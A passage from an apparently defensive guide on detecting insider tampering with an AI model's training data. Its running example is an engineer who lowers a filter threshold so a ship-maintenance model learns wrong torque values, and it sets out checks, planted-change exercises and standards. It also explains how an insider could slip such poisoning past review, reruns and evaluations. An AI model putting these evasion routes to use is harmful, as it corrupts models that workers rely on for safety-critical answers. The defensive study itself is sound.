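| 1 | The team uses version control | A provenance record exists, but it may be unsigned and is easy to forge |
| 2 | The platform preserves the history and records how each version came about | A hosted build service signs the record |
| 3 | The platform continuously enforces the team's rules | Builds can't affect each other or reach the signing key |
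| 4 | Two trusted people review every change | Not defined |

A vendor that claims "SLSA level 3" should say which track it means, because a release can reach build level 3 without anyone reviewing its source. The level also doesn't cover the release's dependencies.

To protect against insiders, a team should aim for SLSA source level 4 and build level 3. SLSA's *Build* levels describe level 2 as a deterrent to employees who could lose their jobs, although forging a record may still be easy at that level. Level 3 is meant to prevent engineers from tampering during a build, but it doesn't cover a malicious insider at the build service.

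SLSA's machine-readable summary lists values only for source levels 0 to 3, so a tool that follows the list exactly can't report level 4. Teams may add their own properties, which could record two-person review.

Two further SLSA tracks were still in draft in November 2026, one covering the machines that run builds and the other how a team brings in dependencies.

### Rebuilding, comparing and logging

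A build is reproducible if two people can compile the same source separately and get identical files. Comparing the files can expose a compromised build service, which that service's own provenance record might not reveal. The team has to use the same version of every tool in both builds, remove details that vary, such as timestamps, and pay for a second build system. The comparison won't detect a harmful change if it is in the source or if both builds use the same compromised compiler.

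Comparing a released package with its source takes less work, and it would have shown the extra line in XZ's build script. Nobody can compare trained weights with source code this way, but a model release also includes a tokeniser, settings and sometimes Python code. An insider could alter one of these after the model has passed its tests. Comparing them with the approved copies takes seconds and would reveal the change, unless someone had also made it to the approved copies.

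Logs show who approved a change, started a build or logged in to a machine. To make edits detectable, a log can include in each entry's checksum the checksum of the entry before it:

hᵢ = SHA-256(hᵢ₋₁ ‖ eᵢ)

Here eᵢ is the new entry, hᵢ₋₁ is the previous checksum, and ‖ joins the two end to end. Changing an old entry changes every checksum after it. An engineer who controlled the whole log could recalculate them all, so the service should send the latest checksum each day to someone outside the team.

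Storing logs is cheap, but reading them takes time, and an unread log only helps after someone discovers the harm. Logs can also lead investigators to blame the wrong person if an intruder used stolen credentials.

### Checking a training run

The manifest of approved data files lets the team detect later changes to those files. The team should also record checksums of the filtered training set, the settings file, the container image and the base model, along with the code's commit and the random seeds. The system that starts the job should calculate these values, because an insider who can edit the training script could make it report the old values.

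NIST's *Secure Software Development Practices for Generative AI and Dual-Use Foundation Models* (SP 800-218A; Booth, Souppaya and colleagues, 2024) recommends tracking the libraries, frameworks and pipelines behind each model. It cautions that the code that defines a model is easier to track and reproduce than the model's final weights.

The Australian Signals Directorate suggests publishing a model's components with instructions so that users can rebuild it and compare checksums. An exact rebuild is difficult for a model trained on GPUs, partly because computers round numbers, so the order in which they add them can change the result. In the common 16-bit format, 2,048 + 1 rounds to 2,048, so adding 1 twice gives 2,048, while adding the two ones first gives 2,050.

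A GPU adds thousands of numbers in parallel, in an order that can change with the timing, the software version or the number of GPUs. A different order can give a slightly different sum, and these differences can grow because each training step starts from the previous step's result. PyTorch has a setting that requires repeatable calculations, but it can slow training, and training stops with an error if an operation has no repeatable version. The setting also doesn't guarantee the same result on different hardware.

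If the data filter uses simple rules and a fixed random seed, the team can reproduce the data preparation exactly. A second person can run the approved code on the approved raw files and should get the same checksum. This check needs no GPUs and catches any edit made outside version control.

For the training itself, a reviewer can rerun part of the job:

1. Save the model at regular intervals, for example 200 times during the run.
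2. After the run, choose some intervals at random. An engineer who knew the choice in advance could leave those intervals alone.
3. For each one, load the model saved at the start and train it to the end of the interval, using the approved code and data.
4. Compare the result with the model that the team saved at that point. Honest repeats of the same interval show how much difference to expect.

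Rerunning 20 of 200 intervals takes about 10% of the original computation. If rerunning an altered interval always revealed the tampering, this check would have a 66% chance of catching an insider who altered 10 intervals and a 10% chance of catching one who altered a single interval. A few poisoned documents might change the weights by less than the normal variation between runs, so the reviewer should also compare data checksums.

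Evaluation by people who did not build the model can catch harmful behavior regardless of its cause. For the ship-maintenance model, an outside engineer could write 100 questions about torque values and check the answers against the original manuals. If the model gave wrong values for 2% of such questions, the test would have an 87% chance of including at least one that it gets wrong. At 0.2%, the chance would be 18%. The team shouldn't see the questions beforehand, because an insider could train the model to answer them correctly.

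### Which checks would reveal the lower threshold?

Which checks can catch the change depends on whether the engineer proposes it openly, with the accurate message about older engines, or secretly edits the filter on the training machine.

| Check | Open proposal | Secret edit |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Second-person approval | Before merging, if the reviewer checks the added pages | Doesn't see the edit |
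| Protected branch and separate owner | Send the change to a data reviewer but don't judge it | No effect |
| Controlled build system | No effect | Prevents the edit |
| Rerun of the filter | Gives the same output | Reveals a different checksum before training |
| Provenance record | Passes, but identifies the commit later | Reveals an unapproved training set before release |
| Partial rerun of training | Finds no difference | May reveal a difference after training |
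| Comparison of the release with its source | Finds no difference | Finds no difference, because the filter isn't in the release |
| Logs | Show who made and approved the change | Show who logged in, if someone looks |
| Outside evaluation | After training, if the questions cover the affected engines | The same |

The technical checks work well against the secret edit but hardly affect the open proposal. An insider who knows about them will probably choose the open proposal, and then only the reviewer can stop the change before training.

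The reviewer needs to see more than the one changed line. An automatic job could run the old and new filters on the same raw files, count the pages the new one adds and show the reviewer a random sample of 50. If 5% of the added pages had a wrong torque value, the sample would have a 92% chance of including at least one of them. Checking 50 pages against engine makers' manuals might take two hours, which is reasonable for a change to the training data but not for every change to the code.

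### An exercise with harmless planted changes

Planted packages test whether a team notices published flaws. Someone can test whether the team would notice an insider's change by making harmless changes of the kind an insider might make.

Two coordinators should run the exercise with management's written permission. They should tell the engineers that such exercises take place, but not when. The dispute over the University of Minnesota's flawed Linux patches shows how much resentment a secret test can cause. The coordinators also need a way to block any release that contains a planted change.

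They could plant these changes over several months:

| Planted change | Check it tests |
| --- | --- |
| A lower filter threshold that admits 20 pages about an invented engine | Whether the reviewer looks at the data |
| An extra edit after a colleague's approval | Whether the platform cancels the approval |
| A scanner exception for an empty folder | Whether the separate owner asks why it is there |
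| An edit to the filter on a test training machine | Whether a rerun reveals a different checksum |
| A test release with an altered settings file | Whether the comparison with the source stops it |
| A test model whose provenance record names another repository | Whether verification rejects it |

The coordinators can test outside evaluation by training a small separate model on the invented pages and seeing whether the evaluators notice. The coordinators should remove each planted change before the real training run starts.

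The coordinators should record who or what caught each change and at which stage. A team loses a few minutes if it catches a change before merging, but may lose a month of GPU time if it catches the change after training. The coordinators should also count the honest changes that reviewers sent back as suspicious, because a team could catch every planted change by rejecting nearly everything.

If reviewers caught 5 of 12 planted changes, the detection rate would be 42%, with a 95% confidence interval from about 19% to 68%. The rate for real insiders is probably lower, because they can build trust first and choose their moment, whereas the coordinators have to keep to a schedule. The team shouldn't punish reviewers who miss a planted change, or people will start warning each other about the exercises.

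### Requirements and advice

Most official guidance on these checks is voluntary. Booth and colleagues use "should" for recommendations and "consider" for weaker suggestions. The Australian Signals Directorate's October 2025 guidance is also advisory, as are the five security levels in RAND's *Securing AI Model Weights* (Nevo, Lahav and colleagues, 2024), which are based on how capable an attacker the protection must withstand.

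The EU AI Act's rules for general-purpose models took effect on 2 August 2025, according to *EU publishes General-Purpose AI Code of Practice* (Hill, 2025). They became enforceable for new models in August 2026 and will become enforceable for existing models in August 2027.

Developers can use the European Commission's *Code of Practice for General-Purpose AI Models* (2025) to show that they comply, but following its measures isn't conclusive proof. CSET, a research centre at Georgetown University, describes the code as voluntary, though companies that sign it commit to its measures. Its safety and security chapter applies only to models with "systemic risk", so it almost certainly wouldn't cover the ship-maintenance model.

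| Document | Status | On scanning | On insiders |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| NIST SP 800-218A | Advice | Evaluate all source code for vulnerabilities, and continuously look for exposed secrets | Limit access, monitor training and changes to models, and consider preventing all human access to weights |
| Australian Signals Directorate | Advice | Scan for malware, test software, check signatures and maintain an SBOM | Give people and programs only the access they need |
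| RAND | Advice | Concentrates on the theft of weights | The third level should withstand insiders |
| EU code of practice | Commitments for companies that sign | Update software regularly, and review code that can reach unreleased weights | Check backgrounds, train staff, test their integrity and look for tampering in training data |

SP 800-218A calls for developers to check all code, whether it comes from people or AI models. It recommends protecting weights in proportion to the risk, with measures such as checksums, signatures and approval by several people. It gives provenance tracking medium priority, below the protection of training data and weights. It also calls for developers to document which parts of a model their security practices don't cover.

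RAND's security levels are easy to misapply to insider changes because they rate how well a company protects its model weights from theft. A company could make its weights very hard to steal and still let one engineer change the training data.

The EU code comes closest to addressing insiders. It calls for background checks on employees and contractors who can access unreleased weights or the systems that control access to them, and it counts sabotage by AI models as an insider threat. It also says to check training data for "indications of tampering" but doesn't specify how, so a company could sign the code and still miss the 0.65.

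The code also commits companies to having independent outsiders evaluate their models for systemic risks, and suggests at least 20 business days for most evaluations. A company can skip this step if the model is similar to one already judged safe, or if it can't find qualified evaluators after an early search. The company may not store or analyse the evaluators' test questions without permission.
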